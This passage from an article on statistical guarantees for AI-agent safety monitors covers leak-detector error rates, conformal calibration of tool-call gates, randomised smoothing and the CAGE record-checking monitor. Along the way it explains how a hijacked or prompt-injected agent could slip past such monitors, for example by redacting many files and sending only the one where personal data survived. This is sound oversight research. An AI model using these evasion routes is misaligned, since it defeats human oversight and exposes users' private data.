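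The researchers left out agent tasks with more than 12 input facts and rules in total, because the linear program couldn't handle them. The tests therefore provide little evidence about precision on long runs. Intercode has no data-sharing actions, so they added one to the end of each sequence.

### What the error rates assume

A measured failure rate applies only to data like the test data. In Uppala's tests, OpenAI's Privacy Filter missed 15% of the personal data in one collection and 51% in another. Rahman and colleagues state that, in general, if a failure rate is at most α on the test data, it is at most α + d on the real data. Here d is the total variation distance between the two data distributions, which is the largest difference between them in the probability of any event. With d = 0.1, a 1% bound becomes 11%, but the engineer rarely knows d.

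The method also depends on the tools failing independently of what an attacker does. Solko-Breslin and colleagues assume this, although they let the attacker inject instructions and know the policy, the tools and their failure rates. They say the assumption could hold if the detector reads only text that the attacker can't influence, or if it is robust to the changes the attacker can make. They don't test whether either condition holds for real detectors.

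The assumption may be reasonable for files that the company's own staff wrote. It fails if a hijacked agent writes the text that the detector reads. If the attacker can make the redaction fail at will, the upper bound on its failure probability becomes 1, and the worst-case risk in the example rises from 0.30 to 1.

An attacker can exploit failures he can't cause. Suppose a hijacked agent redacts 50 files, looks for one in which personal data survived, and sends only that file. If each redaction fails independently with probability 10%, the agent finds such a file 99.5% of the time. The 10% rate applies only to a file chosen before the agent sees the results.

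Finally, the rules must correctly describe what each command does. The researchers assigned every command one of five effects: passing data on, merging it, redacting it, creating a clean file or creating a sensitive one. This is easy for a copy command, harder for `xargs`, which runs other commands, and impossible in advance for scripts that the agent writes as it works. If a script copies a secret but is classified as creating a clean file, the calculated risk can be far too low, however accurate the detectors are. Monitoring system calls, as Tether does, could supply some of the missing information.

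### Why the bound approaches 1 on long runs

Suppose an agent combines 100 files, each with a 1% chance of being sensitive. In the worst case, exactly one file is sensitive each time, and each file is equally likely to be the one, so the result has a 100% chance of being sensitive. That chance is 63% if the files are independent, and 1% if either all of them are sensitive or none are. The individual rates are the same in all three cases, so a monitor that has only these rates must use the worst case and block the action.

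This is a limit of any method that makes no assumptions about correlations, including the exact linear program. Lower error rates only postpone the problem. With a 0.1% chance of error per file, the bound reaches 1 after 1,000 files. Information about correlations can lower the bound, but someone has to establish that it is true. The calculation also becomes slower, because the number of unknowns grows with the square of the number of facts. Solko-Breslin and colleagues suggest asking the user when the calculation takes too long, and acknowledge that users may tire of being asked.

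### Calibrating on whole runs

A developer can avoid adding up the risks of individual calls by measuring how often a whole run causes harm. Yu, Partovi Nia and colleagues (2026), in *G-CARB*, do this with conformal risk control, a statistical method for choosing a threshold from past data. Their gate gives each proposed tool call a score between 0 and 1 and stops the agent at the first call with a score above λ. They replay n recorded runs with different values of λ. Let Lᵢ(λ) be 1 if run i causes harm before the gate stops it, and 0 otherwise. For a risk limit α, they choose the largest λ with

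(1 + L₁(λ) + … + Lₙ(λ)) / (n + 1) ≤ α.

With 492 recorded runs and a limit of 5%, at most 23 of the runs may cause harm. The calculation counts the next, unknown run as harmful too, which gives 24 out of 493, or about 4.9%. If the recorded runs and the next one are exchangeable, meaning that every order of the runs is equally likely, then the next run causes harm with probability at most 5%. Errors within a run can be related in any way, because each run counts only once.

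Guaranteeing a 1% limit takes at least 99 recorded runs, all harmless up to the point where the gate stops them. That is far fewer than the 15,000 trials for a tool that the agent calls 50 times, but the guarantee is weaker. It holds on average over the sets of runs a developer might have recorded, so an unlucky set can produce a threshold with a risk above 1%. For 95% confidence in a threshold fixed in advance, the Clopper–Pearson bound requires about 300 harmless runs.

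Yu and colleagues tested the gate on recorded AgentDojo runs by two small Qwen models. The average share of harmful runs stayed within each limit, but under strict limits the gate stopped almost every run. They also calibrated a gate to limit the share of steps that were harmful. It met its limit, but in three of the four settings reported, as many runs caused harm as with no gate (13.3% in two and 22.5% in the third). A long run with one leak can fit within such a limit because the leak is a very small share of the steps.

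The guarantee counts only harm that the researchers' software detects. One of its leak checks searches outgoing calls for an exact copy of a planted marker, so it may miss a paraphrased leak. This method therefore also depends on a detector with no misses, but here the detector is used to label harm in the recorded runs.

The average error rate can be low even when the rate is high for the arguments that matter most. About 12% of the arguments in Rahman and colleagues' data were targets, such as an email's recipient. If an attacker may control at most 1% of all arguments, the attacker could still control about 8% of the targets. Rahman and colleagues therefore calibrate a separate threshold for each kind of argument. This requires enough examples of each kind. They had only about 91 passwords and other credentials, which is enough to support a limit of about 3% at best.

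A new attack can also break exchangeability. In one test, the attacker's text no longer appeared word for word in what the agent read. A threshold set on earlier attacks let the attacker control 4.8% of targets on average and 60% in the worst case. After Rahman and colleagues recalibrated their method on labelled examples of the new attack, the figure was 0.04%, but the method also blocked or changed 84% of the harmless arguments. The recalibrated threshold is guaranteed only until the attacker changes method again.

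### Guarantees against small changes

Some methods allow for an attacker who can change the input only slightly. *Verifiably Robust Conformal Prediction* (Jeary, Hosseini and colleagues, 2024) replaces each calibration score with the worst score that a change of size ε or less could produce. The guarantee then holds against any attack within ε. The paper tests this method on images and simulated control tasks, where the size of a change is easy to measure. *Ensuring Calibration Robustness in Split Conformal Prediction Under Adversarial Attacks* (Qian and Xing, 2025) calibrates on attacked examples and finds that the error rate then stays close to its target over a range of attack strengths.

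For text, researchers count changed words. Randomised smoothing runs a detector many times on randomly altered copies of a text and uses the share of "yes" answers as the score. *CluCERT* (2025), for instance, masks some words and replaces them with words of similar meaning.

A simpler version, which only hides words, shows where the guarantee comes from. Suppose the detector reads ten random words of a 100-word email each time, and an attacker has replaced three of the 100. The chance that a random selection contains none of the three is

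(90 × 89 × 88) / (100 × 99 × 98) ≈ 0.73.

For those selections, the detector receives the same words as before and gives the same output. The score can therefore fall by at most 0.27, whichever three words the attacker replaced and whatever he replaced them with. If the original email scored 0.9, the altered one still scores at least 0.63.

An engineer could combine this calculation with the Clopper–Pearson bound by counting a test email as a failure unless the calculation guarantees that the detector still flags it after any three word replacements. The resulting bound on the failure rate would hold against every attacker who replaces at most three words, if the original emails are representative. She could then use it as an input to the semidefinite program.

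But a hijacked agent writes the whole email, so it isn't limited to replacing three words in an existing one. Even spelling out Alice's phone number takes nine words, and nine replacements could lower the score by up to 0.63, from 0.9 to 0.27. The calculation also doesn't cover added words. And it guarantees only that the detector's answer stays the same, so if the detector missed the personal data in the original email, the guarantee doesn't help.

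For an agent with a long-term memory, it may be easier to limit how many entries an attacker can write. *SMSR* (2026) adapts the masking argument, which it credits to Levine and Feizi, to an attacker who controls a limited number of the memory entries the agent might retrieve. Those entries can contain anything, but the developer has to make sure the attacker can't add more than the limit.

Guarantees for different parts of an input also can't simply be added together. *Certified Robustness under Heterogeneous Perturbations via Hybrid Randomized Smoothing* (Delattre, Wu and colleagues, 2026) proves that a filter that judges a text and an image together can withstand a certain change to the text alone and a certain change to the image alone, but fail when an attacker makes both.

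### Refusing near the boundary

A small change is easier to define for structured data, such as a record with a source and a number. *CAGE* (Delattre, Wang and Cao, 2026) presents a monitor that allows an action only if it would be safe for every plausible correction of such a record.

In their example, a tool returns a record with the source "credit check" and a risk score of 0.46, and the agent proposes to approve a transaction. For credit checks, the policy permits approval up to a score of 0.60. For sanctions screenings, the limit is 0.52. The source may be out of date, and the true score may be up to 0.10 higher:

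| True source | True score | Limit | Safe to approve? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Credit check | 0.46 | 0.60 | Yes |
| Credit check | 0.56 | 0.60 | Yes |
| Sanctions screening | 0.46 | 0.52 | Yes |
| Sanctions screening | 0.56 | 0.52 | **No** |

A monitor that checked for a wrong source and a wrong score separately would approve the transaction, because neither error alone makes it unsafe. CAGE tests each possible source with its highest possible score and refuses the transaction if any combination fails. The transaction then goes to a person for review.

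Every sound monitor with the same information must refuse here. Let m be the smallest change to the score that makes the action unsafe, for the worst possible source. If the score can be off by up to ε, a sound monitor may allow the action only if m ≥ ε. In the example, m is 0.06 and ε is 0.10. The reason is the same as in Alglave and Cousot's theorem, which requires a monitor to refuse if it cannot distinguish a safe situation from an unsafe one. The only way to refuse less often is to reduce the uncertainty, for example by requesting a fresh score.

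In a test based on real payment data, 6,032 of 10,000 proposed actions were safe according to the record but unsafe under some plausible correction. A program that applied the policy exactly to the record allowed all 6,032, and a language model acting as judge allowed 92% of them. CAGE allowed none when it had the policy's actual rules. On ordinary payment traffic, this version decided 57% of cases without a person. When CAGE had to learn the policy from examples, it decided between 2% and 14% of cases on its own across the payment data and a second dataset.

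CAGE guarantees its result for every record within the permitted range, even if an attacker picks the worst one, rather than calculating the probability of a violation. Errors therefore don't have to be independent of the attacker, but the range must be correct. Delattre, Wang and Cao set ε slightly above the 95th percentile of the errors they measured, so a few errors can still exceed it. The data also had to be fresh, because after about ten seconds too many scores had changed by more than ε. As they allowed older data, the share of wrongly allowed actions rose from 1.8% to 7.1%.

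These ranges make sense for scores, amounts and source tags, but not for deciding whether an email contains personal data. The guarantee also covers only one decision at a time, so over a run of fifty decisions, the chance that at least one record lies outside the range adds up, as a redaction tool's failures do.
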